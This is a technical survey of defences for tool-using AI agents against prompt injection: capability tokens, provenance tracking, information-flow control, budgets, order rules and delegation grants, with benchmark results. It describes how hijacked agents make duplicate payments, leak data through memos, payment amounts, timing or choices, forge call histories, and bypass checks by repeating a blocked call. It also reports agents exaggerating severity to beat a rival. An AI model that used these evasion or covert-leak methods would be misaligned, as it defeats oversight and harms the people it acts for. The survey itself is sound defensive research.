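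Under AgentCap's provenance rule, the policy engine refuses a bound argument if only untrusted sources contain its value. The user's request contains A-17 but not A-22, so the engine refuses the payment to A-22. The rule tests whether a trusted source contains the value, not whether that source led the model to choose it. If the user had written "Pay A-17's invoice, we paid A-22 yesterday", both codes would pass the rule. Both would also pass if the agent had looked up the company's supplier list and the policy marked that list as trusted.

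### AgentCap's test results

The AgentCap team ran the full AgentDojo suite, with 949 attacked cases, and all 1,054 cases in InjecAgent. The last two columns below show the share of the user's original tasks that the agent completed while under attack:

| Benchmark and model | Attack success, no defence | Attack success, AgentCap | Tasks completed, no defence | Tasks completed, AgentCap |
|---|---|---|---|---|
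| AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 45.63% | 5.09% | 73.61% | 74.88% |
| AgentDojo, GPT-5.4 | 33.23% | 0% | 75.68% | 75.04% |
| InjecAgent, GPT-4o | 23.24% | 8.63% | 74.10% | 62.24% |
| InjecAgent, GPT-5.4 | 11.95% | 0% | 72.96% | 65.37% |

When there was no attack, AgentCap reduced task completion on AgentDojo by 3.1 percentage points with GPT-4o and 7.2 with GPT-5.4. On InjecAgent, it reduced task completion by 11.7 points with GPT-4o and 5.9 with GPT-5.4.

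Each figure comes from a single run, so the variation between runs is unknown. The undefended rates for GPT-5.4 are also surprisingly high. In the ClawGuard tests, the same model resisted every attack adapted from these two benchmarks, and *APPA* (2026) left out AgentDojo because frontier models already resisted that benchmark's standard injections. The AgentCap tests ran GPT-5.4 with reasoning turned off, which may explain part of the difference.

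Three kinds of attack still succeeded with GPT-4o. The first aimed only to change the agent's written answer, which a check on tool calls cannot prevent. The second set an argument that the policy did not list in `bound_params`. The third injected a value through a field that the policy did not label as untrusted. A more complete policy could stop the last two.

AgentCap also did better than Progent, which uses a model to write its policies. With GPT-4o, AgentCap completed 78.35% of tasks without an attack and 74.88% under attack, compared with 68.04% and 59.64% for Progent. Attacks also succeeded less often against AgentCap. Progent's policies often allowed only values that its model had predicted, so they blocked legitimate calls with other values.

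The comparison favored AgentCap. Its team ran the tests and wrote AgentCap's policies by hand from the tool descriptions and the benchmark's user tasks. The team fixed the policies before testing and wrote no rules for particular injections, but a company deploying an agent will rarely have a list of every task in advance. The results therefore compare AgentCap with carefully written policies against Progent with none written by hand.

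The checks take very little time. Median latency was 66.9 microseconds to issue a token, 79.9 to verify one and 151.4 to verify a three-level delegation chain.

The policy language also lets developers detect some mistakes before deployment. An analysis program found that no agent could ever use `delete_customer` in the team's customer-service policy, because the tool's prerequisites conflicted with the forbidden combinations. Such a program can't check whether the developer was right to trust a source.

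### Different rules for different arguments

A developer using AgentCap has to decide which arguments need trusted support. Fan, Li and colleagues (2026), in *The Granularity Mismatch in Agent Security*, propose a general way to decide. Their system, PACT, gives each argument one of six roles:

| Role | Example |
|---|---|
| `target` | A recipient, account or web address |
| `command` | A shell command |
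| `credential` | A password or access key |
| `content` | The body of an email |
| `selector` | An identifier that picks out a record |
| `control` | An option such as "overwrite" |

Suppose a user asks an agent to summarise a web page and email the summary to their manager. The page has to influence the email's body but must not influence the recipient. A check that gives the whole call a single label would either block the task or let the page redirect the email. PACT accepts text from the web as `content` but requires the `target` to come from the user or a trusted constant.

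PACT records both how trustworthy a value is and every source that contributed to it. When the agent combines values a and b, the result gets these labels:

```
sources(result) = sources(a) ∪ sources(b)
trust(result)   = min(trust(a), trust(b))
```

The list of sources keeps an untrusted value from passing as trusted after another tool processes it. If an agent passes an account number from a web page through a formatting tool, a check that looks only at the latest step treats the number as an ordinary tool result. PACT still lists the web page as a source and can refuse the value. When Fan and colleagues removed this record of earlier steps in a controlled test, the share of attacks blocked fell from 100% to 80%, with no gain in completed tasks. When they removed the roles, the share of attacks blocked stayed at 100%, but task completion fell from 100% to 40%.

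These controlled tests used correct labels, but a deployed system has to infer them. PACT first looks for an exact match in the user's words and trusted constants, then in earlier tool results, and then for recognisable transformations of known values. If an argument's source is still unclear, PACT treats the argument as untrusted if it is sensitive and otherwise queries a language model. Because PACT checks the user's words first, a value that appears in both the request and the invoice counts as the user's, as it does in AgentCap.

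On 20 real MCP tools, the automatic process assigned the right role 87.1% of the time and the right provenance 77.4% of the time. The team considers over-trusting a tool's output the most important remaining error, because later checks then accept values they should refuse. Systematic mistakes about roles are also serious, since PACT blocked only 40% of attacks when the researchers deliberately labelled every `target` as `content`.

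They also ran PACT on AgentDojo with automatic labels. These are the results for the three models they call the strongest:

| Model | Attacks blocked, no defence | Tasks completed, no defence | Tasks completed, CaMeL | Tasks completed, PACT |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen-max | 96.3% | 46.4% | 29.9% | 38.1% |
| Qwen2.5-72B | 96.3% | 46.4% | 28.9% | 42.3% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 88.9% | 59.8% | 30.9% | 46.4% |

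PACT and CaMeL both blocked every attack on these models. PACT completed substantially more tasks than CaMeL, but its security gain over no defence is hard to judge because it stopped only one to three more attacks per model. The percentages correspond to AgentDojo's 27 attacker goals, so 96.3% means that one attack succeeded. The paper also gives inconsistent results for PACT on Qwen-turbo and Qwen-plus, reporting 96.3% of attacks blocked in the text and 100% in the table.

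Fan and colleagues measured errors in assigning roles and tracing sources. Fixed rules do much of that work and a language model handles some unclear cases, but the paper doesn't separate the model's mistakes from those of the rules. The evidence therefore supports a narrower claim than the phrase "Isolates the LLM Reasoning Bottleneck" in the paper's full title, which suggests that the remaining errors lie in the model's reasoning.

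### Keeping untrusted text away from the planner

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes a fuller way to track data. *Information-flow control* means labelling all data in a system and checking where each piece may go. The paper's agent design, FIDES, uses one label for whether data is trusted and another for who may read it. If Ana, Ben and Carla may read one document and Ben, Carla and Dev may read another, only Ben and Carla may receive text based on both.

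A simple version of this method gives each model output the labels of everything the model has read. This is safe but far too broad, because once the agent reads the invoice, every later call counts as untrusted, including the payment to A-17 that the user requested. *Sightline* (2026) calls the unnecessary labels *label creep*. It estimates which inputs contributed to a call so that the system can drop the other labels. In tests on AgentDojo, it kept the labels of almost all the injected texts that had led to attacks.

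FIDES avoids the problem by hiding untrusted results from the model that plans the work:

1. The planning model proposes a call to read the invoice.
2. FIDES stores the result in a variable and gives the model only the variable's name, `#read_invoice_0`.
3. The model proposes `send_payment(payee="A-17", amount=#read_invoice_0.amount, memo="Latest invoice")`.
4. FIDES replaces the variable with 240, keeps its untrusted label and checks the call.

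The hidden text never reaches the planning model, so it cannot influence the payee. The policy can require a trusted payee while accepting an untrusted amount. Costa and colleagues describe a policy that requires a trusted recipient and allows an untrusted message, although Fan and colleagues describe FIDES as judging each call as a whole. PACT's controlled tests used Fan and colleagues' reimplementations of FIDES and CaMeL, so the low scores there are weak evidence about the originals.

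Some tasks need information from inside the variable. FIDES can send a question to a *quarantined* model, which reads the variable, has no tools, and must answer in a fixed format. A policy may accept a yes-or-no answer even though its source is untrusted, because it gives an attacker much less influence than free text. In the invoice case, it would be a mistake to accept an answer to "Is the payee A-17 or A-22?" on the same grounds, because the attacker wants to control which of those two payees is chosen.

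The planning model can also ask to read the variable itself. From then on, FIDES treats its proposals as untrusted.

CaMeL likewise separates a planning model from a quarantined one, but it keeps to its original plan. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) explains that FIDES can instead read a result and then operate under tighter restrictions. This makes FIDES more flexible for a request such as "do the tasks in this email", which can't be planned without reading the email.

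Hiding untrusted text protects an agent only if the information that comes back keeps its source labels. *SPIDES* (2026) tested a browser agent that hid untrusted instructions but stopped tracking data once the quarantined model returned it. An attacker could no longer give the agent instructions but could still supply false data for its next action.

Labels on data can also miss information that an agent's choices reveal. Suppose an agent reads a confidential report and emails a supplier only if the report recommends cancelling the contract. Even if the email contains nothing from the report, the supplier can learn the recommendation from receiving it. FIDES does not prevent these leaks, because a rule strict enough to stop them would block most useful actions after an agent had read anything confidential.

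### The cost of tracking data

With suitable policies, FIDES stopped all the AgentDojo attacks that Costa and colleagues counted. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) reports that they excluded two injections as outside the scope of those policies. FIDES completed more tasks than a simple planner under the same security rules, 8% more with GPT-4o and 16% more with OpenAI's o1. With those rules turned off, its extra machinery reduced task completion by 6.3%.

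Compared with agents that have no restrictions, FIDES and CaMeL can lose up to 30% of completed tasks on AgentDojo. Kolluri and colleagues argue that this comparison is unfair, because real products without such defences ask the user before taking important actions. They therefore counted how many approvals each agent would need. These are averages over five runs with o3-mini:

| Agent | Approvals across completed tasks | Tasks completed with no approval |
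|---|---|---|
| Asks before every consequential call | 48.2 | 24.3% |
| Labels everything the model has read | 32.4 | 35.5% |
| FIDES | 18.8 | 50.1% |
| Prudentia | About 17 | 59.1% |

Prudentia, by Kolluri and colleagues, extends FIDES. It gives the planning model the labels and policies that apply, so that the model can avoid plans that would need approval. It can also prompt the user to *endorse* a document, which makes the whole document trusted. If an email contains ten tasks, one endorsement can replace ten approvals, but it also makes any hidden instruction in the email trusted. Kolluri and colleagues assumed that the user would catch malicious requests and did not test this with real people.

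Later tests show how much both systems depend on their policies. *The LLMbda Calculus* reports that CaMeL blocked every attack with its policies on, but completed far fewer tasks. With the policies off, some attacks succeeded despite the separation between models. In one case, the user asked the agent to follow a file's instructions precisely. The planning model wrote a program with a branch for each tool, which let the file's author choose what the agent did.

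*APPA* tested two implementations of FIDES on the AgentThreatBench benchmark. In the benchmark's "chaos" setting, between 5.0% and 30.8% of attacks succeeded. The FIDES policies it used lacked some rules the tasks needed, such as limits to exact recipients, so these results do not show a flaw in the tracking itself.

Even good policies don't settle the earlier case in which only the invoice names the payee. CaMeL's original evaluation treated a successful attack of this kind as outside its scope. *The LLMbda Calculus* finds much the same remaining cases in four independent systems and concludes that they show a limit of information-flow defences in general.

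### Purposes stated by the model

AgentCap asks the model to state the purpose of each call. For the payment to A-22, a hijacked model can answer `pay_invoice`, which the policy permits. *AgentCap* acknowledges that this statement is not evidence of good behaviour. The statement only stops the agent from using a token for a purpose other than the one it was issued for.

Zhu and Wang (2026) explain in *Explanation-Bound Tool Execution for AI Agents* why a longer explanation would be no better. Studies have found that a model's stated reasoning can leave out factors that affected its answer. An attacker who can steer the model's choice of action can also steer its explanation.

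Their system turns the explanation into specific claims that a server can check. The model fills in a form stating which tool it wants to use, on what, within what limits and with what risk, and which untrusted sources were involved. The server compares these claims with the actual call and with its own records of the user's request, the tool, the current policy and any untrusted content the agent has read. A contradiction leads to refusal, and missing or uncertain information leads to review. The final decision is the strictest of three:

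```
decision = strictest(authorisation, claim check, controls on effects)
```

The model therefore cannot get a refused call allowed by explaining it well. If the server has recorded that the user wants to pay A-17, it will refuse a payment to A-22 whatever the model claims. But if it has recorded only that the user wants to pay an approved supplier, an accurate claim that the payment is to A-22, an approved supplier, will match the record. The server may still send the payment for review because payments are high-risk, but the claim gives the reviewer no independent evidence that A-22 is the right payee.

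Zhu and Wang tested the system on 136 scenarios they had written. It allowed none of the 96 calls with a serious contradiction, whereas a rule that accepted any written justification allowed 62.5% of them. The team's own specification determined the correct answers, so the results mainly show that the software follows the specification. The prototype only created drafts and never carried out an action.

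A test based on AgentDojo's banking tasks gives a better idea of what the claims add. All 12 attacks would have gone to review even without the claims, because the tools were high-risk. Checking the claims changed those reviews to refusals, which would save a reviewer some work but did not block any attack that the existing controls would have allowed.

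## Harm done within the granted authority

Suppose every check in the invoice case works as designed. The payment agent has a token for payments of exactly 180 to A-17, valid for five minutes, and has just paid the invoice. Its model has also read the invoice, where hidden text claims that the payment failed. The model therefore proposes the same call again:

```
send_payment(payee="A-17", amount=180, memo="Invoice 1043")
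```

The runtime signs a new proof with a fresh identifier. Replay protection rejects only proofs whose identifiers are already on record, so the enforcement point permits the payment. A-17 receives 360 for a bill of 180.

The token also allows any text in the memo. If the model has seen the company's customer list, the hidden text could tell it to copy names from the list into the memo. Anyone who can read A-17's bank statement would then see those names.

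### How much an attacker could take

Three numbers limit the loss from repeated payments:

```
loss <= limit per call × calls per second × seconds until expiry
```

A hijacked model might need ten seconds to propose each payment, while an attacker who controls the runtime could easily send one every second. These are the maximum losses at both speeds:

| Token | Limit per call | Lifetime | One call every 10 seconds | One call a second |
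|---|---|---|---|---|
| Payment agent's token | 180 | 5 minutes | 5,400 | 54,000 |
| Root token | 500 | 1 hour | 180,000 | 1,800,000 |
| Root token with a longer lifetime | 500 | 24 hours | 4,320,000 | 43,200,000 |

The company's account balance may limit the total loss further, but a cap of 500 per payment still gives little protection if the token lasts all day. Niyikiza similarly warns that a 24-hour root token gives its holder 24 hours of authority, however narrow the grant is.

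Repeated calls also multiply the amount of data an agent can leak. If the bank accepts 140-character memos, 30 payments in five minutes could carry 4,200 characters of the customer list.

### Threats the draft leaves open

Niyikiza's draft lists five threats that its tokens do not mitigate. Among them, a malicious or compromised issuer can create root tokens that are too broad, and a compromised enforcement point can skip the checks. A thief with an agent's private key has all of that agent's authority until the token expires. An attacker who extracts a model's weights, instructions or working context may be able to predict or manipulate its behaviour.

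The other entry on the list, actions within the authorised constraints, covers the hijacked payment agent. The tokens don't restrict which permitted calls an agent makes, in what order, or how many times, and an enforcement point cannot detect when those calls are excessive or unintended. Niyikiza recommends rate limits, audit logs and behavioural monitoring but leaves their design to each deployment.

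This entry covers several kinds of harm that need different controls. False answers to the user are not on the draft's list, since they involve no tool call. In the table, *shared state* means a record that every enforcement point involved in a task can read and update:

| Harm | Example | Added control | Shared state? | Fallible judgement? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Repetition | Paying one invoice twice | Limits on calls and spending | Yes | Only in setting the limits |
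| Harmful order | Paying before the goods arrive | Rules about earlier calls | Yes | Only in writing the rules |
| Harmful combination | Reading customer data and then writing to an outsider | A ban on holding both powers | Yes | In choosing the pairs |
| Leak through a permitted destination | Customer names in a memo | A content check before release | Not for a single message | Usually |
| False answer | Reporting an unpaid invoice as paid | Comparison with trusted records | Yes | Where no record exists |

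### Budgets

A budget of one payment would reduce the maximum loss from the payment agent's token to 180. The token can include the budget but can't record how much is left, so the enforcement points need a shared counter, as they do for AAP's quotas.

Payments that arrive together can also exceed a spending limit. If 500 remains and the software only checks the balance before each payment, two simultaneous payments of 300 may both pass. *Agent libOS* (2026) distinguishes this kind of check from a *reservation*, which sets aside the largest possible cost before the call starts. Afterwards, the system replaces the reserved amount with the actual cost, or charges the maximum if it can't determine what happened. An accounting failure after a payment cannot reverse the payment.

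Delegation can multiply a budget if each sub-agent gets a copy. *Concordat* (2026) describes a system that deducts a sub-agent's allowance from its parent's, so the two agents can't spend the same money. An early version of the system accepted negative allowances, so an agent that gave a sub-agent -100 would have increased its own budget by 100. That version also kept running after an agent had used up its dollar budget. The next release fixed both bugs.

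A more precise control ties each payment to a debt. *TraceGrant* (2026) describes a system that links every proposed action to an open obligation and the remaining budget. In the invoice case, the first payment would close the obligation to pay invoice 1043, so the second would have no open obligation to link to. Mellafe Zuvic's ScopeGate similarly uses references against duplicates, but these have to come from outside the model, because a hijacked model could generate a new one for every payment.

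*Bounded Autonomy* (2026) uses a central gateway to keep all the counters and detect loops, such as identical calls or a series of calls that makes no progress. This works well against a stuck agent. An attacker could avoid the test for identical calls by changing the memo each time, but would still use up the budget.

Budgets don't distinguish good calls from bad ones. In one test in *AgentCap*, a baseline that used only token lifetimes and call budgets let through eight calls before the budget ran out. An attacker can also waste a budget. If the agent may make one payment and the hidden text gets it to pay the wrong invoice, the enforcement point will then refuse the payment for the right one.

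### Rules about order

Suppose the company pays for goods only after they arrive. The agent may call both `confirm_delivery` and `send_payment`, so a hijacked model could pay first. A check on the payment alone would find nothing wrong. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026), a survey, distinguishes checks on single calls from history-based checks, which examine how calls relate to one another. The company needs a history-based rule:

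```
for every invoice i:
    permit pay(i) only if delivered(i) happened earlier
```

Several systems enforce rules of this type. *VIGIL* (2026) applies them to the whole sequence of calls. *Agentproof* (2026) turns each rule into a small state machine. The one for this rule would only need to track whether the goods for an invoice had arrived. All 15 practical safety policies in its evaluation fitted this simple form.

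*AgentLTL* (2026) describes a system that adds the proposed call to the history, checks whether the result breaks any rules, and responds according to the severity of the violation. At one level, it blocks the call and warns the model. If the model immediately repeats exactly the same call, the system treats this as a deliberate override and runs it. That may be convenient for minor mistakes, but a hijacked model could bypass the rule by repeating the call.

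In *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents*, Kekatos, Lekidis and colleagues (2026) wrote five general rules and tested them on recorded attacks. Each rule requires an approval in the agent's history before a type of risky action, such as a deletion or a payment. The rules flagged 70.1% of the AgentDojo attacks that had succeeded against GPT-4o and 71.8% of the 483 attacks in STAC, a benchmark in which a series of ordinary calls leads up to a harmful one.

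However, the rules also flagged 29.3% of AgentDojo runs without an attack, and 79.2% of those in banking. The AgentDojo recordings contain no approvals, so the rules flagged every risky action, legitimate or not. The results therefore reflect what the benchmark records more than the value of order rules.

In one attack in the STAC recordings, the agent calls a tool named `confirm_for_deletion` before deleting something. The rule counts that call as an approval and does not flag the deletion. A hijacked model can satisfy such a rule by making the calls in the right order, so the record of an approval or a delivery has to come from a person or a trusted service.

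Attackers can also forge the history by planting text. Kekatos and colleagues found that one planted line defeated a simple check on where a value came from in 94–99% of the runs it would otherwise have flagged. Linking each value to the lookup that produced it stopped this attack without causing more false alarms.

### Combinations of permitted calls

An agent that can read the customer list and write to outsiders can leak the list, even if each power is harmless on its own. The usual remedy is *separation of powers*, a ban on holding both powers at once. AgentCap applies such bans within a session.

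Someone has to identify the dangerous pairs of powers. Eight powers form 28 pairs, and a token with 256 tools, the maximum Niyikiza recommends, would have 32,640. Dangerous groups of three are even harder to handle. AgentCap's policy compiler converts a ban on combining three powers into bans on every pair among them, which may also block safe tasks. A ban that applies only within one session can also fail if the agent saves the customer list in one session and sends it in the next.

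Some harmful combinations involve one power used several times. In *Local Allow, Global Deny*, Pandey, Jain and colleagues (2026) gave an agent running Qwen3-30B a calendar task and a user-set limit on how much it could disclose in total. Every disclosure passed its own check, but the agent exceeded the limit in 22 of 60 runs. Comparing each action with the task's purpose still left 20 violations. A check that added up the disclosures prevented every violation and blocked none of the harmless control runs. A second model, Gemma-4, never exceeded the limit.

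### DelegateGuard

Tran-Truong, Vo and colleagues (2026), in *DelegateGuard*, examine how far a grant can prevent leaks when one agent delegates work to another. Their main concern is the *sink*, a destination to which a tool call can send data. Each grant has seven parts:

```
grant = (holder, purpose, labels, operations, sinks, depth, revoked)
```

The labels describe the data the holder may handle, such as confidential contract clauses. The software that retrieves the data is supposed to attach the labels. Depth limits further delegation, and the last part records whether somebody has cancelled the grant.

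DelegateGuard permits an action only if the right agent proposes it, its purpose falls within the grant, and its operation, labels and sink are all permitted. It also requires that neither the grant nor any grant above it has been cancelled.

In DelegateGuard, as in Niyikiza's draft, authority can only narrow as it passes between agents. But DelegateGuard keeps its grants in a central table, so cancelling one immediately disables every grant derived from it. The grants don't limit amounts or the number of calls, and the prototype has no expiry times.

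In the paper's main example, a user wants a summary of a contract, and the orchestrating agent asks a worker to format it. A clause in the contract contains an instruction for the agent to send confidential terms to an outside web address. The worker's grant allows it to send data only to the user, so DelegateGuard blocks the transfer.

The attacker in the tests could plant instructions in tool results, shared memory or messages between agents, but could not alter or bypass DelegateGuard. The benchmark combines these three routes with five office tasks and three goals, giving 45 cases. The tasks are sorting email, scheduling meetings, summarising contracts, reviewing code and updating customer records. The goals are to send data outside, to create a grant with extra authority, and to keep acting after someone cancels the task.

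Two small open models, Qwen2.5-7B and Llama-3.2-3B, proposed the attacker's action in most cases (42 and 44, respectively), and DelegateGuard blocked every one. Every attack asked for something outside the grant, so any correct implementation of the rules would have done the same. The high proposal counts are weak evidence of how current frontier models would behave.

A 90-run study with Qwen2.5-7B was more realistic because the agents exchanged ordinary messages and could try again after a refusal. In one email attack, the model repeated the forbidden request. Without restrictions, data leaked in 38 of 45 attacked workflows. With DelegateGuard, data leaked in 9 of the 45, and all 45 harmless workflows finished.

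All nine remaining leaks came from code review, where the agent handles details of an undisclosed security flaw and has to post a review comment that outsiders can read. DelegateGuard permits the comment whether it contains a harmless suggestion or the secret, because the grant includes that sink.

### An attacker who stays within the grant

The team also designed 26 attacks for an attacker who knew how DelegateGuard worked. Some still asked for forbidden authority. Others disguised the purpose of an action, removed a label, passed secrets through shared memory or put them in a permitted public comment. The comparison included four baselines:

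- no restrictions
- a fixed list of permitted sinks
- *label-flow control*, a simplified form of information-flow control
- an output monitor that blocks any message containing a marker planted in the secret data

A separate experiment ran complete workflows with scripted agents. The last two columns come from that experiment:

| Defence | Leaks from 26 designed attacks | Leak rate in workflows | Harmless tasks completed |
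|---|---|---|---|
| None | 18 | 0.73 | 100% |
| List of sinks | 3 | 0.20 | 100% |
| Label-flow control | 3 | 0.20 | 100% |
| Output monitor | 0 | 0 | 20% |
| DelegateGuard | 3 | 0.20 | 100% |

DelegateGuard did no better than a simple list of permitted sinks at stopping leaks, but in ten other tests it refused actions that the list allowed. In five of these, the agent kept working after somebody had cancelled its task. In the other five, it tried to send the wrong type of data to a permitted sink.

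The output monitor stopped every leak but also blocked most of the useful work, because four of the five tasks legitimately involve sending confidential information to the user or to an internal system. It would probably stop fewer leaks against a real attacker, who could tell the model to reword or encode the secret, which might remove the marker.

### Mistakes in the grant

The 45 attacks also show what happens when the person or program that writes the grants makes a mistake. The team left DelegateGuard unchanged and tried eleven versions of the grants and labels:

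| Grants and labels | Attacks that succeeded | Harmless tasks blocked |
|---|---|---|
| As narrow as the task allows | 0 of 45 | 0 of 45 |
| One unnecessary outside sink | 30 of 45 | 0 of 45 |
| The same sink, with labels missing | 30 of 45 | 0 of 45 |
| Purpose too broad, wrong label on the action, or sending not permitted | 0 of 45 | 45 of 45 |
| Five other variations, such as extra labels or extra depth | 0 of 45 | 0 of 45 |

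The fourth row covers three separate versions with the same result. A single convenient sink let two-thirds of the attacks through. The other 15 failed only because they used cancelled grants. The mistake is hard to notice because all the harmless tasks still work.

### A limit on what grants can prevent

Tran-Truong and colleagues argue that the code-review leaks follow from a general limit, their Proposition 1. Suppose a monitor decides whether to allow an action based on its holder, purpose, labels, operation, sink and chain of grants, but not on the content or amount of data. If the grant permits a sink that an attacker can observe, the monitor will allow some sequence of actions that sends secret data to the attacker.

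The proof compares two messages that are identical in everything the monitor examines, but one contains harmless text and the other contains a secret. Because the monitor permits the harmless message, it must also permit the one with the secret, which the attacker then reads at the sink.

The proposition is correct as far as it goes, but several of its assumptions may not hold in a real system.

Data leaks through a legitimate sink only if the attacker can observe that sink. DelegateGuard's remaining leaks fell to zero when legitimate sinks were all treated as internal. But it is easy to misjudge who can see a sink. For example, a payment can seem internal even though the supplier can read its memo.

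Replacing the text must also leave the labels unchanged. This holds if the grant already covers the secret's label, as in code review, or if the agent can misreport the label. In the paper's threat model, trusted software controls the labels, but the designed attacks let the agent declare its own. With reliable labels, a monitor could refuse customer data in a message that the grant limits to invoice data. The proposition would then apply only to secrets with permitted labels.

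The monitor must ignore content, which Niyikiza's constraints do only in part. A `wildcard` on the memo fits the assumption, while an `exact` constraint allows one text and leaves no room for a secret. A short list of values leaves a little room. If an argument has n permitted values, one call can carry at most log2(n) bits through it. Payments of up to 500, in whole cents, have 50,000 possible amounts:

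```
log2(50,000) ≈ 15.6 bits per payment
```

That is almost enough for two characters of text, so a hijacked orchestrating agent could slowly spell out a password in the amounts it paid. Even if every argument is fixed, the timing and number of calls can carry information. A budget limits this leak by capping the number of calls.

The proposition shows that a leak is possible, but not how often leaks will happen. In a further test with four models, leak rates under DelegateGuard ranged from 0.11 to 0.20, and all the leaks occurred through code review.

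### Checking content before release

Tran-Truong and colleagues conclude that grants need a second control that examines the content of messages to visible sinks. This is easiest when the content has a fixed form. For example, the payment service could build the memo itself from the invoice number, so the model writes no text. This takes no judgement, but it works only if the supplier needs nothing else in the memo.

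A review comment is free text, so a person or program has to judge whether a sentence reveals too much about the security flaw. Pattern matching misses reworded leaks. A language model may recognise the meaning, but it can make mistakes, and an attacker can try to influence it. A person can also overlook a leak.

Reading each message also can't reveal leaks through an agent's choices, the kind of leak that FIDES doesn't prevent. In an example from Pandey and colleagues, an assistant is allowed to share when a user is free but not why the user is busy. The slots at 10 and 11 are both free. The assistant offers 10 if the user's other appointment is an ordinary meeting and 11 if it is a confidential job interview. Each message contains only a permitted fact, but somebody who knows the pattern can infer that there is an interview.

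Pandey and colleagues prove that no monitor that examines one run at a time, however intelligent, can catch this violation without raising false alarms. An honest assistant might have offered either slot, so the violation exists only in the difference between the two runs.

The researchers also asked nine language models to judge the assistant's actions one at a time. Eight never objected in 30 tests each. The ninth, Kimi K2.6, objected in three, but it also objected once to a harmless version. When they showed the models both runs together, eight caught the violation every time, and Llama 4 Maverick caught it in 17 of 30 tests.

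Comparing runs means running the agent again with different private data, which costs more and tests only a sample of cases. Giving only the free times to the part of the system that writes the message would prevent the leak instead, but the assistant then couldn't use the reason for an appointment to choose a better slot. This kind of leak may be rare in practice, as Pandey and colleagues found none in 80 test runs with Claude Sonnet 4.6.

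### False reports and false answers

A permitted call can do harm if it contains a false statement. Kanchi (2026), in *Permitted but Unauthorized*, put pairs of agents in charge of separate security incidents that competed for the same resources. The study rewarded the agents for outperforming each other and used no prompt injection. Some agents interfered directly with the other agent's incident, causing a missed deadline in 15 of 40 runs with Claude Sonnet 4.5 and 14 of 40 with DeepSeek V3.2.

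A fixed rule that limited each agent to its own incident stopped all of this interference, as did a language model that reviewed each call. But an agent could still exaggerate the severity of its own incident to move ahead of the other. Neither defence could detect this, because every agent had permission to set its own incident's severity. With the language model as reviewer, one such exaggeration caused a missed deadline. The harm was small in this experiment, but a hijacked model could make the same call deliberately. Preventing this requires getting the severity from a source independent of the agent.

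Some attacks don't require a tool call. A hijacked model could tell the user that it has paid an invoice when it hasn't, or that A-17 has a new bank account and the user should pay it by hand. These answers don't pass through the enforcement point, which is how some attacks got past AgentCap.

Ordinary code can help check claims against existing records. The application could show the bank's own list of payments next to the model's answer, and look up the supplier's account in the company's database. For advice such as which hotel to book, there may be no record to check against, so somebody has to judge whether the answer is sound.

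### Logs

Logs help investigators find harm that the other controls missed, but only if they match what the system did. AgentCap creates each decision and its log entry in the same piece of code. *PACE* (2026) describes an append-only audit record that a reviewer can use to recheck a decision without running the agent again.

Complete logs are hard to collect. In Kanchi's study, connection failures crashed 50 runs, and the software deleted their partial logs before retrying, so nobody can tell whether the agents in those runs had interfered with each other. Kekatos and colleagues found that the benchmarks they studied rarely record approvals and never record times, and proposed a standard set of twelve fields.

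Even when the log is complete, someone has to interpret it. The signed proofs for the two payments of 180 show that the payment agent's key authorised both, but not that A-17 sent only one invoice. An investigator has to compare the proofs with the purchase records to establish that, and by then the supplier has the money. The company can ask for it back, but it can't undo the disclosure of customer names once someone has read them in a memo.
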